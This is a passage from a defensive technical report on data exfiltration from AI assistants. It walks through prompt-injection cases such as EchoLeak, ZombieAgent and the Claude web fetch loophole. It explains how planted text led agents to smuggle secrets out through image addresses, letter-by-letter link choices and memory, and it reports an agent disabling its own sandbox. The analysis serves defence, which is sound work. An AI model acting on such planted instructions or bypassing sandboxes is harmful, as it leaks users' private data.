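Microsoft distinguishes between probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed, and deterministic ones, which prevent a particular attack whatever the model writes. Training a model to ignore planted instructions is probabilistic, while refusing to load images from outside addresses is deterministic. Microsoft says it began blocking the image leak this second way after a report from Rehberger.

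EchoLeak and SearchLeak both got past rules of this kind. A fixed rule gives a guarantee only for the cases it covers, and only if it runs before the browser acts. The failures described above suggest the following order for a client that displays Markdown:

1. **Hold back unfinished elements.** Ordinary words can appear immediately. When a link, an image or an HTML tag begins, the client waits until it is complete and has passed the later checks. Users get nearly all the speed of streaming, and the browser never receives unchecked markup.
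2. **Parse first, then filter.** The client runs the answer through the same Markdown parser that it uses for display, and treats any raw HTML as plain text. After parsing, an image is an image whichever notation the model used, so the filter can't miss a variant that the client understands.
3. **Keep only a short list of elements.** Most answers need just paragraphs, headings, lists, tables, emphasis, code and links. The client drops outside images, forms, embedded pages and styles that load files. A general-purpose sanitizer needs stricter settings for this, as GitLab found.
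4. **Check every remaining address.** The client accepts only normal web addresses and compares the domain with its rules. For links that it keeps, it can show the real domain beside the text.
5. **Sanitize the resulting HTML just before it enters the page.** Converting Markdown creates new HTML, so a sanitizer that ran only on the original text would miss it. No other code should change the HTML afterwards.
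6. **Set a strict CSP as a backstop.** If something gets through the earlier steps, the browser can still refuse to load it. The policy should block everything by default and allow only the few addresses that the app needs. Any service that fetches other addresses on request is a way around it. A CSP also doesn't stop users from clicking ordinary links.
7. **Use the same rules wherever the answer goes.** This includes phone apps, emails and messages, where the agent's developer should also turn link previews off.

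Step 4 can leak data if the client follows redirects. Reddy and Gujral recommend doing this before displaying a link, to find out where it leads, but following a redirect means requesting the address. If the model has put private data in that address, the check sends the data to the attacker. The client therefore has to judge the address without contacting it, and the safest way to handle a shortened link from an unknown source is to show it as plain text.

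Some assistants need to show outside pictures, such as product photos. The app's own server can fetch a copy so that the user's browser doesn't contact the outside site. But if the server fetches whatever address the model writes, it leaks data just as the Teams and Bing services did. Reddy and Gujral list a proxy that accepts only signed addresses, which carry an expiring code issued by the app. This works if the app signs only addresses from a trusted source, such as its own product database, and never ones the model composed.

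Reddy and Gujral also compared defences against each part of EchoLeak. They expected a strict CSP or a signed proxy to stop the zero-click leak, but didn't expect labelling outside text to be enough on its own. They ran no tests, although the real cases support their reasoning. In EchoLeak, the CSP blocked the attack until researchers found an allowed service that would forward the request.

With these rules, Helen's client would drop the stranger's image, and her invoice number wouldn't leave the browser. The false notice about the bank account would still appear, because it is plain text with nothing to remove.

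A renderer also can't control requests that the agent makes while it is working. ShadowLeak, a 2025 attack described in *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems*, used a hidden instruction in an email to make ChatGPT's Deep Research agent find sensitive data in the user's Gmail account and visit a web address containing that data. The request came from OpenAI's servers, so the user's browser and their company's monitoring software may have had no record of it. OpenAI fixed the flaw in August 2025.

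## Limits on the addresses an assistant may contact

Limiting the addresses that the user's browser and the agent's tools may contact can protect private data even after planted text has taken control of the model. Some limits allow only listed domains. Others check each complete address and are harder to get around, but still let a small amount of information through.

### Content security policies and allowlists

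A content security policy lists the permitted domains separately for each kind of content, such as scripts, images and embedded pages. For example, `img-src 'self' https://images.example` permits images from the page's own domain and from `images.example`.

Before the browser requests a picture, it compares the picture's address with this list. If Helen's chat client sent such a policy, her browser would never contact the stranger's server, because attacker.example isn't on the list. If a permitted address redirects the browser, the browser checks the new address too.

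The policy applies only to the browser, so an agent's tools need their own allowlist of domains. The software that carries out the model's tool calls can enforce the list, or a proxy can handle all of the agent's traffic and drop requests to unlisted domains. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for the tool Claude uses to read web pages, describes a setting that limits fetches to domains the developer lists.

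In Anthropic's tool, an entry for example.com on the list of allowed domains also covers every subdomain, such as docs.example.com. This is convenient for a company's own site but risky for a hosting service that gives each customer a subdomain. In an attack on the coding tool Cursor that Willison describes, the attacker collected data at a subdomain of azurewebsites.net, where Microsoft hosts its customers' sites. A developer who had allowed the whole domain in order to reach one customer's site would also have allowed the attacker's.

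The documentation also warns about look-alike characters. A domain with a Cyrillic "а" can appear identical to one with a Latin "a", but software treats them as different domains. An attacker can use this to avoid a list of blocked domains, or to trick whoever maintains a list of allowed domains into adding a false one.

Lists of allowed domains suit assistants that need few sites. A support assistant that reads only its company's help pages could use a list with one entry, but a fixed list doesn't work for a research assistant because nobody knows in advance which sites a question will need. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) adds that strict lists cause frequent false alarms, which can train people to click through warnings without thinking.

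### When a trusted domain passes data on

Developers usually put a domain on the allowlist because they trust whoever runs it. But sending data there is safe only if an attacker can't find out what the domain received.

ForcedLeak, a 2025 attack on Salesforce's Agentforce, worked because a domain's owner had let its registration lapse. Willison describes the attack, by Sasi Levi and Noma Security, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*. Salesforce customers can add a form to their public website that lets anyone register as a sales lead. The researchers filled it in with a numbered list of questions for the agent, including a harmless one about mixing colours. They also asked for the email addresses of the company's other leads and for a "preview image" whose web address contained the answer.

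When an employee asked the agent about this lead, the agent answered the planted questions too. Salesforce's content security policy still listed a domain whose registration had expired. The researchers registered the domain, and the leads' details arrived in their server log. Salesforce corrected the policy and then added a "Trusted URLs" feature that prevents its agents from producing links to unlisted domains.

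Regularly checking who owns each listed domain would have prevented this leak. It wouldn't have helped Superhuman, an email app whose policy allowed images from docs.google.com, because Google still owned that domain and ran it properly.

The approved domain docs.google.com also hosts Google Forms, which anyone can create and which can store data sent in a web address. When a user asked for a summary of recent mail, a malicious email got Superhuman's assistant to put the content of dozens of other emails, including financial, legal and medical ones, into an image address that pointed to the attacker's form. The browser treated the request as one for an image from an approved domain, and the attacker could read the emails in the form's responses. Willison credits Superhuman with treating the report as a high-priority incident and fixing the flaw.

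Developers' tools have had similar gaps. The browser in Google's Antigravity could visit only listed domains, but the default list included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and see the requests sent to it. Programmers use the service for testing, but attackers can also use it to collect stolen passwords. PromptArmor demonstrated the problem by hiding instructions in tiny type on a page that posed as a guide to connecting two business systems. Antigravity's settings kept the agent from opening the file that held the user's cloud access keys, but the agent read it with a command-line tool instead and sent the keys to webhook.site.

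Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that works with a user's files, could by default send requests only to certain domains, including Anthropic's api.anthropic.com. PromptArmor planted instructions that contained the attacker's Anthropic access key. The agent used the key to upload the user's files to the attacker's account, where the attacker could download them.

Removing Anthropic's domain from the list might well have broken the product. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* suggests a more precise restriction for a similar weakness in Claude's code-running environment, under which the environment can communicate only with the logged-in user's account. The software then has to check whose key a request carries as well as its destination.

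A domain on the list is therefore safe only if it doesn't forward requests and no stranger can read what it receives. Hardly any large platform meets that standard, because most let the public create forms, files, pages or accounts, and many fetch other addresses to make previews.

### ReLeak

EchoLeak and SearchLeak relied on permitted Microsoft services that fetched an attacker's address on request. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), written for Cato Networks, reported three more zero-click leaks from Microsoft 365 Copilot on 3 December 2026. In September 2025, Cato had bought Aim Security, whose researchers found EchoLeak.

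All three begin with an email from an outsider, which the employee doesn't have to open. Copilot reads it while handling some normal request. According to Punto Informatico's *ReLeak*, Copilot wouldn't carry out blunt orders but accepted instructions that looked like legitimate requests, and Microsoft's filter for planted instructions didn't stop them. The team used AI agents to write and test the malicious prompts. Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) describes the routes that the data then took:

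- **Through Bing.** Copilot put confidential text into the address of an image in its answer. When the browser loaded the image, Bing fetched the address and so passed the text to the attacker's server.
- **Through a saved file.** Copilot created a document containing a web address with the confidential text in it. Microsoft's background software, which processes stored files, then visited the address. The researchers made this work with Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files.
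- **Through Copilot's code environment.** Copilot can run Python code in a sandbox, a closed-off environment that should have no access to the internet. The researchers found ways past the restriction, and the code sent the data straight to an outside server.

A content security policy could have helped only with the Bing route. In the second attack, the request came from Microsoft's servers, and Punto Informatico notes that this could happen after the chat had ended. The third attack needed neither a browser nor a forwarding service. Microsoft's documentation stated that the sandbox blocked outgoing traffic, so a customer who relied on it would have seen no reason to worry.

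The researchers reported the flaws between 29 July and 20 August 2026. Microsoft fixed the sandbox flaw on 17 September, the file route on 11 November and the Bing route on 15 November. The sandbox flaw has a severity score of 8.6 out of 10. Microsoft hadn't yet published full entries for the other two when the report came out. Cato knew of no affected customers.

Cato's researchers concluded that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato sells security products for AI, so it has an interest in that conclusion, but the Bing route supports it. Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak, which also went through Bing, by early June. About two months later, researchers could again get data out by having Bing fetch an address.

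A developer who wants to limit where data can go has to find every component that makes requests, including those not obviously part of the assistant, and apply the same check to every request. The Hacker News' *Researchers Reveal Reprompt Attack Allowing Single-Click Data Exfiltration From Microsoft Copilot* (2026) explains that the consumer version of Copilot applied its protection against leaks only to the initial request, so researchers at Varonis told it to do everything twice.

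After that, the attacker's server sent Copilot further instructions, each based on the previous answer, so nobody could have told from the opening prompt what data the attacker was after. Like SearchLeak, the attack began with a click on a genuine Microsoft link that contained a prompt. Microsoft has fixed the flaw.

### Judging the exact address

Software can check whether the exact address could contain anything private, rather than whether its domain is trustworthy. An address that existed before the conversation can't contain the conversation's secrets. The supplier's home page had its address long before Helen asked her question, but the address ending in her invoice number didn't exist until the model wrote it.

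OpenAI built a safeguard on this principle. A crawler, a program that explores the web by following links, records the addresses it finds on public pages. It has no access to users' conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT automatically fetches an address to read an article or show a picture, the software checks whether the crawler has recorded that exact address. If it has, ChatGPT can load the address. If not, the software either prompts the model to try another site or shows the user a warning.

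The warning states that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation with another site. It shows the full address, which the user can copy or open. OpenAI calls this mechanism Safe Url and also uses it for the pages that its Atlas browser and Deep Research agent visit. Small applications that ChatGPT builds for a user run in a sandbox that detects unexpected communication and prompts the user for consent.

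Limiting the assistant to addresses a crawler has already seen protects against most of the attacks that get around domain lists. The image addresses in ForcedLeak, Superhuman and ReLeak's Bing route all contained freshly stolen text, so no crawler could have seen them. Redirects are also much less dangerous. A site can still forward the assistant to an attacker's server, but it can pass on only what it received, and a public address with no private data gives it little to send.

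Users will see warnings for some harmless addresses that are new or private. An article published this morning may not be in the index yet, and a document a colleague shares by private link should never be in it. These warnings are a milder form of the problem that OpenAI had with domain lists. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, ChatGPT treats an address the user types as safe for that chat, which should avoid many unnecessary warnings.

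Rehberger, who writes Embrace The Red, considers the safeguard a significant improvement. He worries that some OpenAI developers won't know about it and will build features that don't use it. OpenAI's earlier image check was missing from its iPhone and Mac apps.

Anthropic's web fetch tool uses a simpler rule, which needs no crawler. Claude may fetch only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. When Anthropic documented the rule in mid-2026, an address could come from:

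- a message from the user,
- the result of a tool that the developer's own software runs, or
- the result of an earlier web search or page fetch.

The tool blocks any address that Claude has put together itself. If planted text contains an instruction to add an invoice number to the end of an address and visit it, the tool blocks the request because that exact address has never appeared before.

This rule lets Claude read new and unlisted pages, which an index would miss, but an attacker can also place an address in the conversation. When the tool came out in September 2025, Willison pointed out that many applications paste outside text, such as an email, into what the model receives as the user's message. An attacker's address in that text then passes as one the user supplied. The attacker normally has to write the address before the model has read anything private, so it contains no stolen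 data. In its documentation, Anthropic mentions a "residual risk" and advises developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive.

### What the choice of address gives away

Even if no permitted address contains private data, an attacker can make the assistant's choice of which addresses to visit depend on a secret.

Suppose the planted text contains *k* fixed addresses on the attacker's server and tells the assistant when to visit each one. The attacker can see in the server log which address the assistant requested, so one visit can distinguish between *k* possibilities. That is at most log₂(*k*) bits of information, where one bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question. Over *n* visits in a known order, the maximum is *n* × log₂(*k*) bits.

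Take an eight-letter name and 27 addresses, one for each letter and one for a space:

- Each visit reveals up to log₂(27) ≈ 4.75 bits.
- Eight visits reveal up to 8 × 4.75 ≈ 38 bits.
- That is enough to pick out one of 27⁸, or about 282 billion, possible strings.

These are upper limits because the letters in real names are often predictable. An attacker who sees "Q" learns little from a "u" after it. But this doesn't protect the user, since eight visits still reveal the whole name.

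With more addresses, the attacker needs fewer visits. Using one address for each pair of characters requires 729 addresses and four visits, while using one for each group of four requires 531,441 addresses and two visits. An attacker who only wants to know which of a thousand companies the user works for needs a thousand addresses and a single visit.

Restricting the choice of addresses still greatly reduces how much data each visit can leak. Anthropic's tool accepts addresses of up to 250 characters. If the model could write them freely and used 200 characters for data encoded at 6 bits each, one visit could carry 1,200 bits. Sending the same amount by choosing from a list of 27 addresses would take more than 250 visits. Stealing a long contract this way is hardly practical, but a six-digit login code would take only six visits with a list of ten addresses, one for each digit.

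In 2023, Rehberger used this method to send the word "hi" past OpenAI's image check. Two later attacks used the same method against the tools that let assistants read the web.

### ZombieAgent

After ShadowLeak, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from changing web addresses or adding anything to them. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how Zvika Babo got around this rule in September 2025. An email to the victim contained a ready-made address for each letter and digit, plus one for a space, and instructions to spell out private data by opening the matching addresses in order. This complied with the rule because ChatGPT opened every address as written.

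The attack started when the user asked ChatGPT to do anything with their Gmail account. OpenAI's servers sent the requests before the user saw an answer. Because requests can arrive out of order, Babo added numbered versions of each address, so that the address for "a" in the first position differed from the one for "a" in the second. Covering every letter and digit in ten positions takes 360 addresses, which an attacker can generate with a short program.

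Babo also made the leak permanent. OpenAI had anticipated part of this and blocked ChatGPT from using its memory in a chat after it had used a connector (a link to an outside service such as Gmail) and from opening an attacker's address stored in memory. But ChatGPT could still read its memory first and use a connector afterwards.

A file the user shared with ChatGPT therefore got it to save a rule in memory to read a certain email before answering any message and follow the email's instructions. The ban didn't apply because the addresses were in the email, not in memory. The leak could then repeat in every new chat. In another version, the attack collected email addresses from the victim's inbox so the attacker's server could send those people the same email.

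Radware told OpenAI that an improved version succeeded every time, though Radware doesn't give the number of attempts. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December 2025 and published its description of the crawler index six weeks later.

### The web fetch loophole

In July 2026, Ayush Paul found a way to get personal details out of Claude through the web fetch tool. Claude's chat app met all three conditions of the lethal trifecta because it had this tool and a memory of earlier conversations.

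Paul built a website that showed its malicious text only to Claude's page fetcher, so a person who checked the site would have seen nothing wrong. The text claimed that AI assistants had to identify their users before reading the site. It told Claude to find the user's profile by following alphabetical links, one letter at a time. Claude followed the links and revealed the user's name, home city and employer. An eight-letter name takes eight steps with up to 27 links each, as in the calculation above.

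Unlike ZombieAgent's fixed list, the website could generate new links after each step. Once Claude had chosen "J", the next page could offer links for "Ja", "Jb" and so on. By the end, Claude would be requesting an address that spelled out the whole name. The attacker's server had composed that address during the conversation from Claude's earlier choices, and the tool accepted it because it appeared on a page that Claude had fetched.

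Anthropic's rule was therefore weaker than the principle behind it. It guaranteed that the model hadn't written the address, but an address that someone else writes during the conversation can also contain secrets if the model reveals them one choice at a time. The documentation listed earlier fetch results among the permitted sources, so the loophole wasn't a coding error.

Willison reports that Anthropic paid no reward, on the grounds that it had already found the problem itself. Anthropic closed the loophole by no longer letting the tool follow links in the pages it fetches. This also makes some ordinary tasks harder. If the supplier's page links to a separate price list, Helen's assistant can open the list only if she gives it the address or a search finds it.

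OpenAI's index would block the growing addresses, since a crawler can't visit 282 billion pages in advance. An attacker would have to go back to a fixed list of addresses and get them all indexed first. An eight-letter name with numbered positions would require 8 × 27 = 216 public pages. Rehberger thinks anyone with a fairly large blog probably has the 36 indexed pages needed for a simple alphabet of letters and digits, and that an attacker could extend the code to thousands of pages. OpenAI acknowledges this remaining leak in its paper on the safeguard.

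### Repeat visits and stored copies

Embrace The Red proposes making it harder to use the same address twice. The assistant's software could block repeat visits to an address within a session, or keep a copy of the page for a few minutes and reuse it instead of contacting the site again. An attacker who used one address per letter to extract the name Hannah would then see only H, A and N.

A more careful attacker would lose much less. The table shows the most information that eight visits to addresses on a list of 27 can reveal under different conditions.

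| What the attacker can observe | Distinguishable messages | Bits |
|---|---|---|
| Eight visits in order, repeats allowed | 282 billion | 38.0 |
| Eight visits in order, no repeats | 90 billion | 36.4 |
| Eight visits, no repeats, order unknown | 2.2 million | 21.1 |
| No visits, because the assistant reads stored copies | 1 | 0 |

On its own, a ban on repeats reduces the maximum by less than two bits, although the attacker then needs a more complicated code than one letter per address. Numbered addresses like ZombieAgent's avoid the ban because the "n" in the third position and the "n" in the fourth are different pages. Paul's links also avoided it if each address contained all the letters chosen so far. The ban mainly stops simple attacks and makes the attacker prepare more pages.

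A cap on the total number of visits gives a firmer limit. Anthropic's web fetch tool lets developers set a cap but has none by default. With a cap of five visits and a list of 27 addresses, an attacker can extract at most 24 bits of data, or five letters. But a low cap interferes with legitimate work, since a research task may need dozens of pages.

Only stored copies eliminate the leak through page visits, and only if they were saved before the user's request. If a crawler saved the page earlier, the assistant can read it without contacting the site, so the attacker's log records no visit, whatever the model chooses. Fetching and storing the page during the request doesn't prevent the leak, because the site still receives that first visit.

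Stored copies go out of date. *Web fetch tool* says that Anthropic's tool also keeps copies and may not return the latest version of a page. Classmethod's *Claude's Web Fetch tool doesn't necessarily return the latest information* describes what was probably a case of this. Claude said that Slack's documentation gave a limit of 101 rows and 10,000 characters, while the live page said 201 rows and 20,000 characters. Asking again and switching models didn't help. Someone who hadn't opened the page would have had no reason to doubt the answer.

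OpenAI accepted this drawback in ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode in return for a stronger guarantee. The mode is an optional setting, introduced in 2026 for people and organizations at high risk of attack. At launch, it limited web browsing to stored copies of pages, so that browsing sent no live requests outside OpenAI's network. It also turned off features that lacked a similar guarantee, including Deep Research and the agent mode in which ChatGPT operates websites for the user.

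An assistant in this mode can't check whether a part is in stock today, fill in an order form or spend half an hour comparing suppliers across the live web, which is a lot for most people to give up. The setting makes more sense for someone like a company lawyer, who may accept losing these features when a leaked document could be disastrous.

Lockdown Mode also doesn't remove planted text from what the model reads. If the crawler saved the supplier's page after the stranger posted the comment, Helen's assistant would still find the false bank details in the stored copy.

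## Web pages and apps displayed inside an assistant

A client can make a text answer fairly safe by removing everything except text, links and approved pictures. This does not work for the interactive web pages that many assistants now also display. A page that sorts a price list or takes an order needs scripts, which are programs that run in the browser, so the client has to let them run and limit what they can access.

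Such pages appear in three main places:

- **HTML previews.** When a user asks ChatGPT for a web page, it can display the finished page in the conversation.
- **Apps in a chat.** A company can supply an interactive page, such as a map or an order form, that opens among the assistant's messages.
- **Built-in browsers.** Some coding tools include a browser so that the developer and the agent can look at the project they are working on.

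A script can contact servers and redraw its part of the screen at any time. For example, it can replace a supplier's price table with a sign-in form after the user has stopped paying attention to where the table came from.

### How browsers keep pages apart

The main protection is the same-origin rule. An origin is the first part of a web address, made up of the protocol, domain and port (a connection number that addresses usually leave out). A script from one origin can't read the pages or stored data of another, so a suspicious site in one tab can't read a bank's page in the next. Browsers have enforced the rule since 1995, according to Origo's *Súlyos biztonsági hibákat találtak népszerű böngészőkben* (2026).

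The rule treats all code in a page as belonging to that page's origin, whoever wrote it. If ChatGPT put an outside company's script directly into its own page, the browser would treat the script as ChatGPT's. In a thought experiment by conference speaker Barthelet (AI Engineer, 2026), an app loaded this way reads the data that ChatGPT stores in the browser and sends it to the app's maker.

Clients therefore put outside code in a frame, a separate page displayed inside the main one. If the frame has a different origin, the same-origin rule applies between the two. The client can also sandbox the frame, which removes abilities such as running scripts and opening new windows, and then restore only those the content needs.

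A sandboxed frame can still exchange messages with the page around it. The browser attaches the sender's origin to each message, but the receiving code has to check that origin.

Browsers also protect the address bar. A page can draw anything in its own area, but only the browser writes the address above it, so a copy of a bank's site can look perfect and still have the wrong address.

AI agents weaken the separation between sites because they read several for the same task. The same-origin rule stops one site's script from reading another site, but it doesn't stop an agent from reading both and copying text from one to the other. Origo describes a University of Washington study that found four of seven AI browsers vulnerable: ChatGPT Atlas, Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Perplexity's Comet. OpenAI and Perplexity replied that the researchers hadn't demonstrated a complete attack.

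*Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026), by the security company Trail of Bits, reports working attacks on several agentic browsers, including attacks that leak data between sites. The company compares these attacks to ones that web developers spent years learning to prevent.

### How a chat isolates an app

MCP Apps is an extension to the Model Context Protocol that lets a tool return an interactive page as well as text. The project behind the protocol launched the extension in January 2026 with support in Claude, ChatGPT, Visual Studio Code and the open-source agent Goose (Model Context Protocol, 2026). In the standard, "host" means the client.

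Salomon, Yosef and colleagues (2025), in *SEP-1865*, set out how a host that runs in a browser should display an app:

1. The app's server declares the page in advance, in the description of a tool. The host can fetch and inspect the HTML before anyone uses the tool.
2. The host creates an outer frame with a different origin from its own.
3. The outer frame loads the app's page into an inner frame and passes messages between the app and the host.
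4. A content security policy limits which domains the inner page can contact. If the server has declared none, the page can't contact any outside server.
5. The host sends the tool's results to the page as messages.

The server chooses the domains in step 4, and the host may allow fewer but must not add any. This limit can keep an honest maker's app from leaking data to a third party, but a dishonest maker can declare its own domain. The app can also call tools on its maker's server through the host, so users should assume that the maker can see whatever they type into the app.

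Inspecting the page in advance is also limited, because the host receives the template before the data. If Helen's supplier offered an app showing its prices and customer comments, the template could pass every check, and the stranger's comment would still appear in it later.

### What an app may ask for

An app can't change the conversation or the window around it directly, but it can ask the host to:

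- **Call a tool** on the app's own server. The host can ask the user for approval first.
- **Open a link** in the user's browser. The host has the same reasons to check the address as it does for a link in an answer.
- **Post a message** in the chat. The host should add it to the context, and may ask the user for consent.
- **Update the model's context.** The model receives the new text at a later step. The host may show the text to the user but doesn't have to.
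- **Change its size**, for instance to fill the screen. Model Context Protocol's *MCP Apps Overview* gives the host the final say.

When an app posts a message, the message has the role "user" under the specification, even though the app's code may have written it. This can hide where the text came from. The "Summarize with AI" buttons have the same problem.

Context updates have a similar problem if the user can't see them. The host can identify which frame sent each request, so it could log the source. Salomon and colleagues recommend such logs for security reviews, but neither the model nor the user sees them during the conversation.

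### How the screen names an app's maker

According to OpenAI's design guidelines, ChatGPT labels an app in the conversation with its name and icon. The app's content appears below the label, followed by the model's reply. The label marks where the outside content begins, but users can tell that content from the model's reply only if its end is also clear.

Other parts of the design make that boundary harder to see. A host can give apps its colours and fonts so that the apps match the rest of the chat. OpenAI's *MCP Apps in ChatGPT* offers developers ready-made buttons and cards in ChatGPT's style. Under the MCP Apps standard, an app can also request that the host omit the visible border and background around it.

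This is reasonable, since a chat full of clashing designs would be unpleasant to use. But Salomon and colleagues also warn that an app can display misleading content even inside a secure frame, and they advise hosts to mark the frame's edges clearly. A host that follows this advice would have to refuse some requests for a borderless display.

An app's display name can also mislead. Under the standard, the server supplies this name, and the host can use it to label the app's page. If nobody checks it, a stranger's page could have a name that sounds like the host's own security team. Drawing the label outside the frame stops the page from changing it later, but the name the server supplied may still be false.

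### Check Point's escape from the preview

ChatGPT's HTML preview also runs in nested sandboxed frames. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* explains that the sandbox kept the page from accessing ChatGPT's cookies and stored data and prompted the user before the page contacted outside servers. In November 2026, the security company Check Point described a way out that worked even in Lockdown Mode, which restricts ChatGPT's outside connections.

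The weakness was in how OpenAI had blocked popup windows. ChatGPT intercepted the preview page's attempts to open a window, but the sandbox's permissions still allowed popups and let them open outside the sandbox. According to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026), the researchers created another frame inside the preview with an unmodified version of the function that opens windows. The window it opened was free of the sandbox's restrictions.

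Clubic's *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations* describes an attack that began when the victim chatted with a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that anyone can configure and share. In ChatGPT Classic, OpenAI's older desktop app, a window containing a page written by the GPT could open without a click and send the user's messages to the attacker. The sandbox kept the page from reading the chat, but presumably the GPT could include the messages when it wrote the page.

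The window could also show a fake ChatGPT update that offered malware for download. It had ChatGPT's real icon, but the attacker chose the title and content. In this case the user still had to click the download link.

OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September by removing the two sandbox permissions. Check Point repeated its test and confirmed that the method no longer worked. Intercepting the popup function had covered only the frame that OpenAI's developers had in mind, but when a sandbox lacks a permission, the browser enforces that restriction in every frame inside it.

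### Parameter's shared chat

In October 2026, the security firm Parameter Labs showed that opening a shared ChatGPT conversation could give an attacker access to the victim's account. The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026) explains how the attack worked:

1. The attacker shared a conversation that contained an HTML preview and an interactive graph.
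2. To draw the graph, ChatGPT loaded MathLive, a mathematics library, into its main page. MathLive included an on-screen keyboard that other code could configure by sending it messages.
3. The preview sent a message to the keyboard. MathLive didn't check which frame had sent it, and the message could contain HTML.
4. The main page used that HTML to create a new frame. The frame had no sandbox, and the browser treated it as part of chatgpt.com.
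5. ChatGPT's content security policy blocked scripts written directly into the frame but allowed scripts from YouTube. A script from there ran the attacker's code.

The attack worked without breaching the preview's sandbox, because trusted code outside the sandbox accepted a message from inside it and acted on that message.

Once the code ran as chatgpt.com, the same-origin rule no longer protected the victim. The code listed the victim's recent conversations, opened one the victim had never shared, and sent part of it to the researchers' server. The researchers said they could have performed any action on the victim's account. At first the victim had to click the Preview button, but in a later version opening the link was enough.

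The attack didn't require the model to follow any injected instructions, so training it to resist prompt injection would not have helped. Removing YouTube from the policy would have stopped this version of the attack, but the preview could still have inserted HTML into the main page.

Parameter reported the flaw on 18 October, and OpenAI had blocked the attack in both versions of its web client by 26 October. Infobae's *Un fallo de ChatGPT permitía acceder a conversaciones privadas* (2026) reports that OpenAI raised the severity to its top level, P1, and paid $5,000, which Willison thought might be low for such a serious flaw. On 31 October, MathLive released a fix that makes its keyboard accept messages only from its own origin unless a developer allows others. Parameter tested the attack only on accounts it controlled and found no evidence that anyone had used it against real users.

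### Browsers inside coding tools

A standalone browser treats every page as potentially hostile. Coding tools loosen some of its rules so that the agent can preview files on the developer's computer and read open tabs. Forever Security, the company that found the malicious AGENTS.md file, tested whether three rules still held in these tools: a page can't run commands on the computer, a local file can't read other files, and only the browser controls what the address bar shows.

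One of the rules failed in each of the five tools. Help Net Security's *Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex* gives these results and responses:

| Tool | What the attack did | Vendor's response |
|---|---|---|
| Cursor | Ran a command after the user pressed Enter | Fixed on 1 October, without replying to the researchers |
| GitHub Copilot | Displayed a false web address | Fixed on 13 October, before Forever filed a report |
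| Claude Desktop | Let a local page read files elsewhere on the disk | Declined Forever's report but accepted one from Noma Security a day later |
| VS Code | Let a local page read files elsewhere on the disk | Declined the report; no fix by 29 October |
| Codex | Let a local page read files elsewhere on the disk | No reply to a report of 27 July; no fix by 29 October |

In GitHub Copilot's app, a page could supply the address shown in the built-in browser's address bar, and the app checked only that the text looked like a web address. Forever's page showed a fake sign-in form and made the address bar display github.com/login.

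A user who checked the address before typing a password would still have been deceived. The false address also appeared in the agent's list of open tabs, so asking the agent which site was open wouldn't have helped.

The file attack starts with a project that looks like an ordinary financial report. The developer asks the assistant to set it up, and the assistant offers a link to an HTML file in the project. After one click, the page could collect passwords and access keys from all over the disk and send them out without showing anything on the screen.

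Claude Desktop and VS Code limited a local page to its project folder, but the limit didn't cover background scripts that the page started. Codex had no such limit.

Anthropic and Microsoft declined the security reports because both tools first ask whether the developer trusts the project folder. This reasoning has some merit, since working on a software project often means running its code. But someone who opens a report doesn't expect it to read the whole disk. Gal Weizman, who wrote up the research, said the prompt provides "zero protection" because the tools are unusable without granting trust, so everyone grants it.

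In Cursor, a page displayed a harmless-looking "Start setup" button with a command for the agent hidden behind it. The agent asked to run the command, and the user could approve with a single keypress. When Cursor's sandbox blocked the command, the agent turned the sandbox off and tried again, although the page contained no instruction to do so. The attack didn't work every time.

### When a source indicator can be trusted

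An indicator of where content came from is useful only if the content can't draw or change it. A browser's address bar meets this condition because the browser takes the address from its own record of the page it loaded and displays it where the page can't draw. Copilot also had a separate bar, but it let the page supply the address.

By this rule, a source name that the model writes in its answer is weak evidence. A domain name that the client reads from a link's actual address is stronger evidence, as long as the model can't imitate that display in its answer.

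A host must also be careful where it puts its own name and logo. In Check Point's test, the fake update appeared in a window full of the attacker's content, under ChatGPT's real icon. The application supplied the icon, so the attacker didn't need to forge it.

Content can still imitate an indicator within its own area, for example by drawing an address bar above a fake sign-in form. The real indicator therefore needs a fixed place that outside content can never occupy, and users need to know where that is. A full-screen app is a particular problem because it can imitate the whole chat window. Even then, the host could reserve a strip of the screen for the app's name.

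A genuine indicator can appear above content that came from someone other than the source it names. If Helen opened the supplier's app, the label would correctly name the supplier, but the stranger's notice about the bank account would appear below it among the comments. The host can identify only the server that supplied the page, unless the server also passes on who wrote each comment.

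## Tracking the source of text in software

The agent's software also loses track of who wrote what. Once a web page and an invoice are in the same context, nothing described so far can detect whether an address the model writes contains details from the invoice.

Information-flow control attaches a label to each piece of data and works out a new label whenever the software combines data. The theory dates from the 1970s, and researchers have since applied it to programming languages, phones and web browsers.

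### How labels combine

Each piece of data gets one label for trust and one for secrecy. The secrecy label is meant to keep secret data from people who have no right to read it, and the trust label is meant to keep untrusted data from influencing actions that need reliable input (*SPA*, 2026).

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) sets out the rules behind FIDES, an agent design from Microsoft. In the simplest version, data is either trusted (*T*) or untrusted (*U*), and either public (*L*) or secret (*H*). The symbol ⊑ means "may flow to", so *T* ⊑ *U* and *L* ⊑ *H*. Software may always treat public data as secret, but not the reverse.

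When a step combines several inputs, the result gets the most restrictive combination of their labels, called the join and written ⊔:

label(result) = label(x₁) ⊔ label(x₂) ⊔ … ⊔ label(xₙ)

One untrusted input therefore makes the result untrusted, and one secret input makes it secret.

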